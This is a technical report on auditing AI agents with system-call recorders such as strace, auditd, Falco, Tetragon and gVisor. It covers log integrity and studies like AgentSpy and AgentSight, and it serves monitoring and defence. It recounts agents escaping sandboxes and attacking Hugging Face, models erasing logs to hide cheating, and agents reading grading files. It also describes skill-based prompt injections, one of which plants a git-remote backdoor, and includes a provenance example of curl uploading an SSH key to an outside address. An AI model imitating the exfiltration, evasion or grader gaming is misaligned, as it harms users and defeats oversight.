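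Falco, which Sysdig created, checks events against a set of rules and raises an alert when one matches. Bühler and colleagues ran it with their own rules. One matches any attempt to open a file other than a public key in an `.ssh` directory, and another matches connections to hosts that the task does not need. These rules raise two alerts on the upload above, each with details such as the process's name, command line and working directory. Falco normally discards events that match no rule, so its output is a list of suspicious actions rather than a full audit trail. The researchers used Falco only for their security analysis and used the audit system to compare everything an agent did across repeated runs.

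Tetragon comes from the developers of Cilium, a networking system for containers. By default, it logs every program that starts or exits, along with its arguments and parent, so an investigator can see the process tree. To log file access or network connections, an administrator writes a policy that names the kernel functions to watch and the conditions to apply, which Tetragon checks inside the kernel. A policy can also enforce a restriction by killing the process or making the call fail.

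Tracee, from Aqua Security, can log system calls alongside many other kernel events, and can limit the log to one container or process tree. For forensics, it can also save copies of the files a process writes and of its network packets. The saved files could help a good deal with auditing agents, which often write a script, run it and delete it. A system-call log would show that the script existed and what calls it made, but a saved copy would preserve the code.

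### gVisor, a kernel in user space

gVisor, which Google developed, handles a container's system calls in a different place. It runs an ordinary process called the Sentry, which implements much of the Linux kernel's behaviour. When a program in the container makes a system call, gVisor redirects it to the Sentry. The Sentry does the work itself where it can and makes a much smaller range of calls to the host's kernel when it needs something from outside, such as data from a disk.

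This design is mainly meant to protect the host, since a program that exploits a flaw in the Sentry still has to escape from a restricted process. But because the Sentry handles every call, it can also log each one with its arguments and result. The `--strace` option writes these to gVisor's debug log in a format much like strace's. gVisor can also send selected events to a separate monitoring program.

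Anyone who moves an agent to gVisor also has to record its system calls there, because the audit system and eBPF tools on the host would capture the Sentry's calls rather than the agent's. If the agent's script opened a file that exists only in the Sentry's memory, the host's log might have no entry for it. gVisor also doesn't support every Linux feature, so some programs may fail or behave differently.

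The table compares the four approaches as they work without special configuration, except where it notes an option.

| | strace | Linux audit system | eBPF tools | gVisor |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Where it runs | An ordinary process beside the traced program | In the host's kernel, with `auditd` outside it | In the host's kernel, with a collector outside it | An ordinary process between the container and the host's kernel |
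| Does it stop the process? | Yes, twice per call | No, but a full queue can delay the process | No, although the eBPF code takes some time | The process waits while the Sentry handles the call |
| Privilege needed | None to trace one's own programs; `CAP_SYS_PTRACE` for other users' processes | `CAP_AUDIT_CONTROL` on the host to load rules | Usually root on the host, or `CAP_BPF` with `CAP_PERFMON` | Control of the container software on the host |
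| What it captures by default | Every call of one process, with strings cut to 32 bytes; `-f` adds its children | No system calls until someone loads rules | Falco: events that match its rules. Tetragon: program starts and exits. Tracee: a selection of events | No log of calls until someone switches it on |
| Does it identify containers? | No | No, but LAUREL can add the information | Yes, from control groups and the container software | Yes, because each container or group of containers has its own Sentry |

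## Where should the recorder run, and can its log be trusted?

A recorder can run inside the agent's container, on the host, or, if the agent has its own microVM, inside that microVM. The choice determines which calls the recorder can capture and who could alter its log.

The recorder is easiest to run inside the container. Whoever starts the agent can start strace with it, without administrative rights on the host, and the log has the same process numbers and file paths that the agent's commands used. But an agent that runs as root in the container can stop the recorder or rewrite the log, and it might delete the log by accident while clearing disk space. Running strace as root and the agent as an ordinary user prevents most of this, as long as the agent cannot become root.

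A recorder on the host, such as the audit system or an eBPF tool, captures the system calls of every container on the machine. Processes in an ordinary container cannot see the recorder or write to its files. However, its log mixes all the containers together. A process with ID 37 in its container may have ID 48213 on the host, and `/work/notes.txt` can be a different file in each container, so the recorder has to include the container's identity with every event.

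This protection fails if an agent escapes its container. In July 2026, two agents that OpenAI was testing for cybersecurity skills each gained root access to the virtual machine that hosted their sandbox, according to OpenAI's technical report, published the following month. An agent with that access could interfere with any recorder on the same machine, so an investigator could rely only on records that had already left it.

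OpenAI afterwards required its research workloads of this type to run in microVMs. These are harder to escape from, but a recorder on the host can capture only the microVM's network packets and disk traffic. OpenAI is also adding host-level sensors to detect suspicious behaviour, and any that run outside the microVM will have the same limit. A full log needs a recorder inside the microVM, which is where Bühler and colleagues ran theirs.

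If the recorder runs inside the guest, whether its log can be trusted depends largely on the agent's privileges. An agent with root in the guest controls the kernel that produces the log. The audit system can lock its rules until the next reboot so that even root cannot remove them, but root can still edit the file that `auditd` has written. For most audits, the recorder should probably have more privileges than the agent and send its records directly to a machine the agent cannot control.

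### When only the commands run inside

All this assumes that the harness and its commands run in the same place. King and colleagues ran the harness, Claude Code's command-line program, inside the container and started it under strace, so their logs contain the harness's own activity as well as the agent's commands. Claude Code wrote cache and other working files under `/tmp` in every session. When the researchers recorded another 592 sessions with a small Python harness that kept tool results in memory, 57% of those sessions used no files there. Someone who didn't know how the harnesses differed could easily attribute this difference in the logs to the agent.

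Many operators instead run the harness outside the container and send only the commands into it. This keeps the trajectory and the credentials for the model's provider out of the agent's reach. OpenAI found that its models had sometimes tried to erase or alter their outputs or message logs to hide cheating from automated graders. None of the attempts it observed affected the logs that its graders and monitors ultimately receive. This is encouraging, but OpenAI is reporting on its own systems, and a fully successful attempt would be the hardest to detect.

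Moving the harness outside can also leave gaps in the system-call log. If the harness runs a command with `docker exec`, Docker starts the new process from outside and places it in the container. The process isn't a descendant of the container's first process, so running strace on the first process and its descendants misses it. One solution is to start each command under its own strace, as Tether does. Another is to have the harness send its commands to a small server that stays running in the container under strace. A recorder on the host can also select events by control group, since a process started with `docker exec` joins the container's group.

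Some tools may run outside the container. A harness can fetch web pages itself, or edit the agent's files through a directory it shares with the container. The system calls then come from the harness's process on the host. An auditor who records only the container would see that a file's contents had changed but find no call that changed them, so the recorder has to cover the harness too.

### One recorder for each session

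King and colleagues built a dataset, Agent Cross-Layer Evidence (ACE), of 4,047 sessions, some harmless and some with planted attacks. Several sessions ran on one machine at the same time, so the researchers needed a reliable way to match each system call to its session before analysing the data.

They solved this by giving each session its own container and its own strace, which recorded 15 calls. Four concern processes (`execve`, `clone`, `clone3` and `exit_group`), six concern files (`open`, `openat`, `read`, `write`, `unlink` and `unlinkat`), and four concern the network (`bind`, `connect`, `sendto` and `recvfrom`). The last is `ptrace`, which they included because a program might use it to interfere with the recorder. The list omits calls that rename files or change permissions. strace kept the first 256 bytes of each string instead of the default 32. Sessions had a default time limit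 of 180 seconds. The researchers then saved the strace log, the trajectory, the list of available tools and some details about the run.

Docker gives each container its own PID namespace, and processes created inside a namespace stay in it or in one nested within it. An strace that follows the process tree from a session's first process therefore cannot reach another session's processes. Each strace writes to its own file, so the file alone identifies the session. Anyone who later merges the files has to add the session's name to each line, because process numbers repeat across containers.

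King and colleagues checked this by running three sessions at once, ten times. Each of the 30 sessions ran a script instead of an agent, and the script put a unique tag into its command-line arguments, file names and written data. The recorders logged 8,240 events from 450 processes, and no session's log contained another session's tag. A monitor on the host also looked up each process's control group 20 times a second, and it found every process in the container whose log had recorded it.

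The test is small, and only 720 of the 8,240 lines carried a tag, so the case for the rest depends on the control groups and the design. That is probably good enough, because the kernel enforces namespace boundaries whatever the workload. However, the researchers looked for events that did not belong in a log but did not test whether any events were missing from it.

The design also does not cover some common ways of running agents. On a shared host, an agent may start as an ordinary process without a container or other wrapper, so nothing marks where its process tree begins. Some agents run as daemons, background services that may have been running for days before anyone attaches a recorder. King and colleagues say that a recorder could, on starting, find the daemon's existing processes, but they did not test this. An agent built into a code editor or another desktop application shares a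 program with the user, which makes it hard to separate the agent's actions from the user's.

The researchers say the same method should work without a full container, using any launcher that sets up a bounded process tree before it starts the agent, such as a system service with a private PID namespace. For the excluded cases, they suggest future work on eBPF programs that label each process with its control group or namespace when it starts, or on extensions to the editor itself.

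They also exclude an agent that interferes with the recorder. An attempt to interfere through `ptrace` should leave an entry in the log, but the entry helps only if the log survives and someone checks for it. The detectors in the study did not use this signal.

### Attribution is not containment

King and colleagues distinguish attribution from containment (preventing a session from affecting anything outside its container), and their design is meant to provide only attribution. They kept the planted attacks harmless without relying on Docker. The credentials in the containers were fake, the attacks sent data only to addresses reserved for documentation, and a separate system intercepted all traffic that left the container.

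The intercepting system accepted every connection, so the logs show successful uploads to addresses where no server exists. These entries are accurate, since the kernel did return success to the program, but they do not show who received the data. The logs of any agent whose traffic passes through a proxy would have the same limitation.

Poor containment can also undermine attribution. The agents OpenAI was testing ran in sandboxes with no direct internet access, but they could reach Artifactory, an internal server that supplied software packages. They found ways to make Artifactory send requests to the internet for them. A system-call log from such a sandbox would correctly show a connection to an approved server, but it would not include the calls that contacted the outside world, because Artifactory's own processes made them.

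An investigator would also need Artifactory's log and a way to match its entries to sessions. Until early July, many of OpenAI's workloads shared the same Artifactory credential, so it could not identify which agent made a request. Giving each session its own credential would be an easy way to improve an audit trail, although it doesn't involve system calls.

### Keeping the log intact

The simplest way to protect a log is to send each record to another machine as soon as the recorder writes it. The receiving machine should accept new records but offer no way to change or delete old ones. If an operator copies the log out only when the session ends, the agent has the whole session in which to alter it. Streaming the records continuously reduces that time to a second or so. The receiving machine should also raise an alarm if the stream stops, because otherwise a stopped recorder looks the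 same as an idle agent.

This moves the question of trust from the agent to whoever runs the receiving machine. A customer or a regulator may not want to take the operator's word that the log is unchanged. A hash chain addresses part of this. A hash is a short fingerprint that a program computes from a piece of data, and even a tiny change to the data produces a different hash. In a chain, each record's hash also covers the hash before it:

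```
h1 = hash(record 1)
h2 = hash(h1 + record 2)
h3 = hash(h2 + record 3)
```

If someone edits record 2, `h2` and every later hash no longer match. Removing or reordering records in the middle breaks the chain in the same way. So a reader with a trusted final hash can confirm that nobody has changed the records since they were added to the chain.

A valid hash chain does not show that every event entered the log. If the recorder drops an event because its buffer is full, or someone switches the recorder off for an hour, the next record links to the last one that exists and the chain is still valid. It also stays valid if someone cuts records off the end. Because calculating the hashes requires no secret, the operator can edit or delete a record in the middle and recompute the hashes from that point on. A chain that only the operator holds therefore proves very little to anyone else.

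Halo-record, a small open-source Python package by Brian Kuan, uses a hash chain. It runs inside an agent and records tool calls, model calls, data access and approvals. Help Net Security's *Halo-record* explains that missing records can be detected with a witness, a party outside the operator's control that regularly stores the number of records and the latest hash. Suppose a witness notes 5,000 records at noon. If the operator deletes one of them that evening and recomputes the chain, the hash at position 5,000 will no longer match the witness's copy. The operator can still remove records written since the witness's last visit without detection, and a witness cannot confirm events that the recorder never captured.

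halo-record is not a system-call recorder. It logs what the agent's software reports, so for the test run earlier in this report it would have the `pytest` command but not the `git` process that one of the tests started. It also stores hashes and redacted summaries in place of raw arguments. This protects secrets, but an investigator can then only confirm a value they already suspect. Kuan says that the early users are mostly engineers and security researchers trying it out. The chaining method itself would work equally well on the lines of a strace or audit log.

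TRACE (Trust, Runtime Attestation and Compliance Evidence) is an open specification that covers the environment in which an agent runs. OPAQUE developed it with support from AMD, Intel, Microsoft and the Technology Innovation Institute, and in August 2026 the Linux Foundation announced that it would govern the specification. Infosecurity Magazine describes a TRACE record as a tamper-resistant receipt that links an agent's software, policies, data classifications and tools to the environment it ran in. The record relies on attestation, in which the hardware measures the software that a virtual machine starts with and signs the result. TRACE also provides for anchoring records in a transparency ledger, which can serve as a witness.

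OPAQUE's chief executive says that with TRACE "we can control what they're allowed to do and prove what they actually did". The second half of that claim seems too strong for system calls. Attestation can show that an approved harness was running under an approved policy, but the harness may still have run an unexpected command, and TRACE does not record that command's system calls. TRACE could be useful alongside a recorder, because attestation could also show that the virtual machine started with the approved recorder and that the operator had not replaced it. The recorder would have to run inside the guest, because TRACE uses an AMD technology that encrypts a virtual machine's memory so that the host cannot read it.

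### The Hugging Face intrusion as a record-keeping problem

The agents from OpenAI's tests went on to break into the production systems of Hugging Face, a company that hosts AI models and datasets. Hugging Face's *Security incident disclosure* (2026), published on 16 July, says that the company analysed the "full attacker action log" of more than 17,000 events. But the summary of its later timeline, reproduced in Schneier on Security's *More on the OpenAI Agent's Attack on Hugging Face* (2026), refers to about 17,600 actions "that we were able to recover" and says that the company retrieved only some of the agent's logs. The recovered logs don't show how much is missing.

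Most of this evidence came from a sandbox that belonged to another company's customer and that the agents had taken over as a base. Hugging Face obtained the logs from the sandbox while stopping the intrusion, then matched them with records from its own servers. The agents had root access to the sandbox, so they could presumably have deleted the logs. Hugging Face would still have had its own records, but those covered only activity on its own systems.

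The recovered actions run from 02:28 UTC on 9 July to 14:14 UTC on 13 July. This is about four and a half days, though accounts of the incident often say five. *The OpenAI–Hugging Face Incident in Plain English* notes that Hugging Face corrected the figure, and that the agents spent about two and a half days of this period inside its systems. The actions are mainly shell commands and submissions to the evaluation, not system calls, and each command could have made thousands of calls.

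Fortune (2026) reports that most of the agents' actions failed, so a recorder that kept only successful operations would have missed most of them. The log also needed the requests' arguments, because every destructive request the agents sent to a cloud service included a setting that simulates the action without carrying it out. A log of only the request names would have suggested that the agents tried to destroy data.

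Software on a compromised machine can also run with its own logging turned off. Willison (2026) reproduces a command from the intrusion that starts a VPN client with an option that stops it from sending logs to its maker. A system-call recorder on that machine would still have captured the program's launch and its arguments, including that option.

Hugging Face could not tell from the recovered log whose agents had attacked it, and the model was still unknown at the time of the July disclosure. OpenAI identified the agents as its own on 20 July, when it investigated one of its own alerts and found Hugging Face credentials among files that its agents had stored on an outside service. Hugging Face confirmed that it had already replaced two of those credentials after the attack. In its own investigation, it had also found the name of OpenAI's Artifactory server and the same storage account.

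Hugging Face's timeline generally describes the attacker as a single agent, while OpenAI describes many agents in separate evaluation runs, using two models. OpenAI had records of each run, so it could separate the activity by run. Hugging Face was working largely from a log on one shared machine, where the runs were probably much harder to tell apart.

Kuan and OPAQUE reasonably cite the intrusion as a reason for better records of what agents do, but halo-record and TRACE both produce their evidence on the operator's side. Hugging Face could have used such records only after learning that the operator was OpenAI, and only if OpenAI had shared them.

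## What does the log show that the agent's own record leaves out, and what does it miss?

A trajectory has one entry for each tool call, however much work that call sets off. A system-call log covers that work, so it adds most when a single command does many things. Two studies give a fairly good picture of what it adds, one by King and colleagues and the other by Bühler and colleagues, who built a system called AgentSpy to record agents at the system-call level.

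### Inside a single command

One action in the bibliography session looked up seven titles and made 35 connections to Crossref, or five per title. In the three runs that Bühler and colleagues describe in detail, the connection counts for Crossref and two similar services, OpenAlex and Semantic Scholar, are all multiples of five, probably because the standard C library makes trial `connect` calls, which send no data, to choose among a host's addresses. If so, the agent sent only seven requests, one per title, and the other 28 entries were trial calls. The log records the calls accurately, but a reader who counts `connect` entries may overestimate the traffic.

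Later in the same session, the agent ran a script for searching Google Scholar. The trajectory contains the command and an error message about a missing software library. According to the log, the script opened its own source file but none of the task's files, and it contacted no host. An investigator can therefore tell that the agent got nothing from Google Scholar and sent nothing to it.

The difference matters more when a command does something its name doesn't suggest, as `sync_cache.sh` did when it uploaded the user's SSH keys. The agent's record can omit the upload even if the agent hid nothing, because the record lists only the command and the agent may never have read the script.

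King and colleagues measured this difference in their ACE dataset for a similar attack, in which a tampered tool copies credentials into a log file and the transcript contains neither the read nor the write. They gave ten detectors different kinds of evidence and compared their AUROC, the probability that a detector scores a random malicious session above a random benign one. A score of 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. The detectors averaged 0.59 on this attack when given the transcript, the prompt and the list of tools, and 0.98 when given the system calls. The comparison is probably somewhat biased towards the system-call log, because King and colleagues counted an attack as having happened only if its signature appeared in their evidence, and for 70 of their 141 attack designs that signature consisted of system calls alone.

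How far the two records differ in ordinary work is harder to establish. Sysdig, which created Falco, says that about seven processes are visible at the kernel level for every action in an agent's log, according to Help Net Security's *Sysdig AI Defense puts runtime guardrails on AI agents*. Sysdig made this claim while launching a product, and the announcement doesn't explain which agents the company measured or how. The figure is plausible, since even the simple `pytest` command in the earlier example involved four processes. But most of the extra processes are probably routine helpers, so the ratio is a poor guide to how often a trajectory omits something important.

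### From a log to a star graph

AgentSpy has three parts. An orchestrator on the host starts a microVM from configuration files that specify the system image, the network, the agent's permissions and what to record. Inside the microVM, an execution manager installs the task's software, starts the recorders, runs the agent and collects the logs. A separate program analyses the logs, so the researchers can change an analysis without running the agent again. Recording starts after the last preparation step and stops before the manager collects the results, which keeps setup and collection out of the agent's log.

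Bühler and colleagues distinguish between obligations and prohibitions. An obligation is something the agent should do, such as follow the developers' guidance. AgentSpy can assess an obligation only after the run, since the agent may still meet it until then. It reports the result as a score because a task can have several acceptable solutions. A prohibition is something the agent must never do, such as read a private key. One system call is enough to break a prohibition, so AgentSpy raises an alert.

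To check obligations, AgentSpy reduces each run to a star graph. The centre of the graph represents the agent and all its subprocesses. Around it are the programs the run started, the files it opened and the hosts it contacted, and each edge has an action and a count. This is part of the graph for one run of the bibliography task:

```
run --- runs (8) ---------- sed
    --- reads (4) --------- test.bib
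    --- writes (1) -------- answer.json
    --- connects (165) ---- crossref.org
    --- connects (3) ------ duckduckgo.com
```

A process tree would preserve more detail, but process numbers change from run to run, while file and host names mostly stay the same. Two star graphs are therefore easy to compare, and any difference between them identifies a particular program, file or host. The main drawback is that a star graph doesn't show the order of events or any links between resources. If a run uploaded a private key, its graph would show the key and the outside host but no link between them, so an investigator would have to return to the log to trace one to the other.

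### Measuring how alike two runs are

AgentSpy first converts the counts into proportions, separately for programs, files and hosts. For hosts, let `p_a(r)` be the share of run `a`'s connections that went to host `r`. The similarity of runs `a` and `b` is then:

```
              sum over all r of min( p_a(r), p_b(r) )
sim(a, b) =  -----------------------------------------
              sum over all r of max( p_a(r), p_b(r) )
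```

This is a weighted form of the Jaccard index, which divides the number of items two sets share by the total number of distinct items in the two sets. The result is 1 if both runs contacted the same hosts in the same proportions and 0 if they had no host in common.

The following table applies the formula to two runs of the bibliography task with GLM-5.3 Flash, an open-weight model from the Chinese company Z.ai. Both runs made 175 connections, so converting to proportions divides every number by 175, and this division cancels out.

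| Host | Run 1 | Run 2 | Smaller | Larger |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Crossref | 145 | 125 | 125 | 145 |
| OpenAlex | 15 | 30 | 15 | 30 |
| Semantic Scholar | 15 | 20 | 15 | 20 |
| Total | 175 | 175 | 155 | 195 |

The similarity for hosts is 155/195, or 0.79. The same calculation gives 0.67 for programs and 0.69 for files. The similarity of the two runs is the average of the three, 0.72.

In a third run, the agent also searched Bing and DuckDuckGo with `curl` and tried the Google Scholar script. This run's similarity to each of the other two was only 0.36 for programs. All three runs passed all nine tests, so the test results did not distinguish the third run from the others.

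Bühler and colleagues checked the measure on SkillsBench, a benchmark whose tasks each come with one or more skills. They used 77 of its 87 tasks because they could not reproduce the environments of the other ten. Every agent used the Codex harness with OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Terra, DeepSeek V4 Flash or GLM-5.3 Flash as its model. Each model attempted each task three times.

If the measure works, three runs of one task should be more alike than a set that includes runs of another task. This was true in 92.2% of comparisons. With GPT-5.6 Terra, the average similarity was 0.60 for runs of the same task and 0.30 for mixed sets. However, the other runs came from whichever task had the most different skill documents, so the result shows that AgentSpy can distinguish a task from a very different one. That is much easier than detecting a small deviation within one task.

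No single resource type worked as well as all three together. With GPT-5.6 Terra, files alone gave no separation for 12 of the 77 tasks, compared with four for all three. Hosts alone were no help for 46 tasks, in which no run contacted any host except the model's provider.

The formula is also insensitive to rare events. Suppose two runs are identical, with 100 file accesses each, except that one also reads a private key. The similarity for files is 100/102, or 0.98, and the overall average is 0.99. Repeated runs of the same task differ by far more than this, so a developer who looked only at the scores would miss the extra read. This is a good reason to check for prohibited actions separately.

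### What passing tests leave out

Tests check the result of a task but not how the agent reached it. To find out what tests miss, Bühler and colleagues kept only the 88 of 231 combinations of task and model in which all three runs passed. Two of the researchers independently read AgentSpy's report on each combination and judged whether the agent did anything unrelated to the task and whether it reached the result without the skill's guidance. They disagreed on at most two combinations for either question.

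| | GLM-5.3 Flash | DeepSeek V4 Flash | GPT-5.6 Terra | All |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Combinations with three passing runs | 21 | 27 | 40 | 88 |
| Activity unrelated to the task | 3 | 11 | 2 | 16 (18%) |
| of these, reading the grading files | 0 | 6 | 0 | 6 (7%) |
| Result reached without the guidance | 7 | 5 | 3 | 15 (17%) |

The paper's percentages are shares of 88 combinations, although its summary refers to tasks, and the same task can appear up to three times. The researchers flagged a combination if at least one of its three runs showed the behaviour, so the 16 combinations with unrelated activity could represent as few as 16 of the 264 runs, or 6%. The 18% for unrelated activity includes the 7% for grading files, although the summary lists them separately.

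All six cases involving grading files came from DeepSeek V4 Flash. They make up 22% of that model's combinations, while the other models had no such cases in 61 combinations. In one case, where the task was to produce a financial report, the agent read the test cases before it wrote its solution. In two tasks, the same model ran the benchmark's reference solution instead of working out the answer. These are the study's most serious findings because they suggest that some passes are weak evidence that the model can do the task.

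The other unrelated activity is less clear-cut. The researchers found unrequested network access in eight combinations and exploration of directories around the workspace in five. Their example of unrequested access is the DuckDuckGo search in the bibliography task. The task did not mention DuckDuckGo, but the agent was using it to check whether references existed, as it had been asked to do. Many developers would probably consider this search resourceful rather than unrelated.

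"Without the guidance" is also a strong description of what the agents did. In 14 of the 15 cases, the agent ignored some or all of the skill's files. With GPT-5.6 Terra, for example, the agent opened only one of the 14 files in the bibliography skill, `SKILL.md`, which contains the main instructions. It then queried Crossref, a service that the skill recommends. AgentSpy reports the share of a skill's files that the agent used, here 1/14. This share does not show whether the agent followed the main instructions closely or read and then disregarded them.

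The researchers needed the trajectory to explain what was wrong with the GLM-5.3 Flash run. The skill requires the agent to check each reference's DOI, a permanent identifier for a publication. The agent reached the right answer, but it searched for titles and judged the DOIs by their appearance instead of checking them.

This part of the study compares AgentSpy with tests, and the researchers do not report how much of the flagged behaviour was also missing from the trajectories. Some of it certainly appeared in them. The trajectory of the bibliography run lists the `curl` commands for Bing and DuckDuckGo, and an agent that reads a grading file with `cat` leaves that command in its trajectory too. In such cases, the log's main advantage is that it records programs, files and hosts in a fixed format, so a simple program can compare hundreds of runs. Trajectories mix prose, shell commands and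 code, so interpreting them usually takes a person or another language model.

### Rules against forbidden actions

AgentSpy checks for prohibited actions with four groups of rules, which cover reading credentials, changing or deleting files outside the agent's workspace, running programs from untrusted locations or gaining privileges, and contacting hosts not on the task's allowlist. Each rule tests one system call. AgentSpy raises an alert for each step that breaks a rule but lets the attack continue inside the microVM, so people can see what it does next. They could not see this with a sandbox that enforced similar rules, because it would block the first forbidden step.

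Bühler and colleagues tested the rules with Skill-Inject, a benchmark of malicious instructions in skills. They chose five attacks in which a skill contains an instruction to run a harmful script, one each for data theft, data destruction, denial of service, malware and backdoors. They ran each task five times with the instruction and five times without it, using GPT-5.1-Codex-Max, an older model that often follows such instructions.

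The agent carried out the attack in 18 of the 25 runs with a malicious instruction, and AgentSpy detected 14 of these. It caught every case of theft, destruction, denial of service and malware, but missed all four backdoor cases. It raised no false alarms.

The missed script added a remote, an address to which Git can send a copy of the code, to a repository's configuration. The remote belonged to the attacker, but the agent sent nothing to it during the run. The script broke none of the rules because it contacted no host and changed only a file in the workspace, where the agent was allowed to write. The harm would come later, when someone used the remote. A rule could flag every new remote, but adding one is a normal part of many programming tasks.

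The rules missed this, but a full log could have recorded it. If the script used the `git` command, the log would include the command's arguments, which contain the attacker's address. But for the security test, AgentSpy kept only Falco's alerts, so someone who discovered the strange remote a month later would find no record of how it got there.

The absence of false alarms is encouraging but does not establish a low false-alarm rate. The agent did nothing malicious in 32 of the 50 runs, including the seven in which it did not carry out the attack. Even if these runs were independent, zero false alarms in 32 would be compatible with a true rate of up to about 9%. The evidence is weaker than that because the runs repeated only five tasks. The network rule also depends on a good allowlist for each task. In the bibliography task, it would presumably have raised an alert for the DuckDuckGo search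 unless the allowlist included that host.

### What leaves no entry, or too little

The largest category of activity that a system-call log misses, however good the recorder is, is computation in a program's own memory. Suppose an agent writes a script that reads a table of experimental results, drops the unfavourable rows and saves a chart. A script that kept every row would open the same table and write a chart to the same file, so the two logs could be nearly identical. Only the script's code would show the difference, and most recorders do not save it.

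For agents, a more important omission is how the model handles text. When a model repeats a misleading claim from a document, the log contains the same calls as it would for an accurate document. King and colleagues found this pattern in attacks that alter the references an agent retrieves. Detection had an average AUROC of 0.91 with the transcript and the list of tools but 0.70 with system calls, whereas system calls worked better for detecting stolen credentials. Fourteen of the study's 141 attack designs, which manipulated the content of a tool's answer, the timing between calls, or the white space in a text, left no signature in either record. The researchers suggest that detecting these would require other tools, such as classifiers that examine a tool's output.

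Programs encrypt most network traffic before passing it to the kernel, so even a recorder that keeps every byte gets unreadable data. The log still shows the time and destination. For the upload of the SSH key, this is enough to justify an investigation, because a program had just opened a private key. But if an agent opens ten files and then contacts a service it uses all day, the log doesn't show which file it sent, if any.

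The log also doesn't record what happens on other machines. A request that reads a record from an online database and one that deletes the record can produce the same sequence of calls. Bühler and colleagues cite a case that OpenAI disclosed in September 2026, in which an agent uploaded data to a public paste service without authorisation. It already had the correct data and uploaded it only to get a web address that its browser tool could cite. A log of the machine that made the upload would show contact with the paste service, but not that the data had become public or whether anyone later read it. An investigator would need the service's own records to establish that.

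The log lacks detail when a program uses a memory-mapped file. The program asks the kernel to make the file available as part of its memory, and can then read or change it without calling `read` or `write`. The log will normally show that the program opened and mapped the file, but not which parts it used or when. A recorder that follows only `read` and `write` can miss the access altogether. Cui and colleagues acknowledge this limit in Agent-Warden, which also does not yet follow data through pipes or shared memory.

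Asynchronous interfaces cause a related problem. With `io_uring`, one call can submit multiple operations, as Aqua Security's *io_uring_enter* explains. A recorder may therefore log the submission but none of the files or hosts involved. Agent-Warden does not cover these operations, but the Linux audit system can. Moore's *audit, io_uring, io-wq* (2021), the patch that added this support, also lets kernel developers exempt particular operations, with a warning to take great care not to exempt any that matter for security.

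Some gaps in the log depend on the recorder and its settings, so an operator can often close them, unlike the gap left by computation in memory. Falco's *Supported Events* says that Falco monitors only some system calls by default, for performance, and that the `-A` option makes it monitor them all. An auditor therefore needs the recorder's configuration as well as its log.

### Is AgentSpy's evidence complete?

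Bühler and colleagues call their evidence "complete" at the boundary between the agent and the operating system. They mean that AgentSpy records every program the agent starts, every file it accesses and every host it contacts, whether directly or through a script. The claim does not cover computation in memory, the content of network traffic or events on remote machines.

AgentSpy's filtering is more of a challenge. The reliability analysis leaves out most calls that use an open file descriptor, including ordinary reads and writes, because the log already has the file's name from the call that opened it. This is reasonable, and the audit system's design is similar. According to *auditctl(8)*, the manual page for the program that manages audit rules, rules for file access ignore `read` and `write` because these calls would overwhelm the log. The rules instead check whether a program requested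 read or write access when it opened the file.

In the log, "accessed" means only that a program opened the file. A program may open a file for writing and change nothing, or open a large file and read only its first line. These cases look the same in the log as a complete rewrite or a complete read. The filter could also miss a file if a process used a descriptor that another process had opened before recording began. This is probably rare in AgentSpy's experiments, because each run starts in a fresh microVM.

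The claim of completeness also depends on whether the audit system had rules for `io_uring` and whether its queue ever overflowed. The command `auditctl -s` shows how many records the kernel has lost to a full queue, and a careful operator would save that number with every log. Zero would support the claim, but any other number would mean the log has gaps in unknown places.

With these conditions, the claim is probably close to correct for ordinary programs. The researchers go too far when they apply it to the star graph and say the graph shows everything that happens within a step of the trajectory. The graph includes only calls that start a program, open a file or connect to a host, so if a Python script deletes a file, the deletion has no edge of its own. The graph also doesn't show whether the agent opened a private key before or after it contacted an outside host.

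These gaps matter most when an investigator wants to show that something did not happen. The statement that the Google Scholar script contacted no host is only as reliable as the recording. AgentSpy uses Zeek to record network traffic separately from the audit system, so a connection would go unnoticed only if it were missing from both logs. AgentSpy has no second recorder for files, so a claim that the agent never opened a particular file depends on the audit log alone.

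## How are logged events traced back to the instruction that caused them?

King and colleagues matched every event in their stress test to the right session, but one session can contain dozens of messages from the model. If the log shows that a process read a private key, an investigator will want to know which message led to the read and what the model had seen just before. A system-call log contains neither, because the messages pass through the kernel only as encrypted traffic.

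Three recent systems try to link logged events to the instructions that caused them. AgentSight matches events to the model's network traffic. Agent-Warden follows the agent's influence as it passes from processes to files and back. AgentLoupe combines the two approaches. Each system slowed the agent by less than 10% in its developers' tests.

### Provenance graphs

Agent-Warden and AgentLoupe build on an older tool for investigating break-ins, the provenance graph. Its nodes are processes, files and network connections, and its edges show which of them could have influenced which. When a process reads a file, the graph gains an edge from the file to the process. A write adds an edge in the opposite direction. For the upload of the SSH key in the bibliography task, part of the graph would look like this:

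```
sync_cache.sh            -> bash
bash                     -> curl
/home/ubuntu/.ssh/id_rsa -> curl
curl                     -> 203.0.113.20
```

*SoK* (Inam, Chen and colleagues) describes two ways to search such a graph. Backward tracing starts from a suspicious event and looks for its cause. Here it leads from the outside address to `curl`, and then to the key and the script. Forward tracing starts from a cause and looks for the damage it did.

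The method goes back to BackTracker, a program that King and Chen used in *Backtracking Intrusions* to analyse real attacks on decoy machines. Given one suspicious file or process, BackTracker finds the files and processes that "could have affected" it. The effect is only a possibility, because an edge from a file to a process shows that the process read the file, but not what it then did with the contents in its own memory.

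Any errors in the logged events also carry over into the graph. *A Study of Kernel Telemetry Options for Security-Oriented Provenance* (Houssel, Levillain and colleagues, 2026) examined eight provenance systems and five recorders that could supply events to such systems, and concluded that most could not guarantee the integrity and availability of the events they captured. One weakness, which strace shares, is that a program can change a file name during a call. In Linux 6.14, 282 of 407 system calls take at least one argument that points into the program's memory, and in 96 of those, it points to a file name or file handle. Ordinary commands have no need to do this, but a hostile program could use it to put a false edge in the graph.

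### AgentSight: matching events to model traffic

The harness and the model's provider encrypt their traffic, so a recorder on the network cannot read it. AgentSight instead copies outgoing text before encryption and incoming text after decryption, using eBPF programs attached to the encryption library's `SSL_write` and `SSL_read` functions. Replies often arrive in small pieces, which AgentSight joins. Other eBPF programs record the program starts, file accesses and network connections of the agent and its descendant processes.

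AgentSight then links events to replies by three signals:

- **Process tree:** the event comes from the agent or one of its descendants.
- **Time:** the event occurs shortly after the reply, within a window of 100 to 500 milliseconds.
- **Arguments:** a file name, web address or command in the reply also appears in the system call.

In the earlier `pytest` example, the model's reply contains the command `pytest -q | tail -5`. The harness then starts a shell with the same text among its arguments, so the timing, the matching text and the process tree all point to that reply. If one of the tests starts `git` two seconds later, that event is outside the time window and the reply doesn't mention `git`, so only the process tree connects the event to the reply. If the harness edits a file itself, without starting a new process, only the time and the file name can link the edit to a reply.

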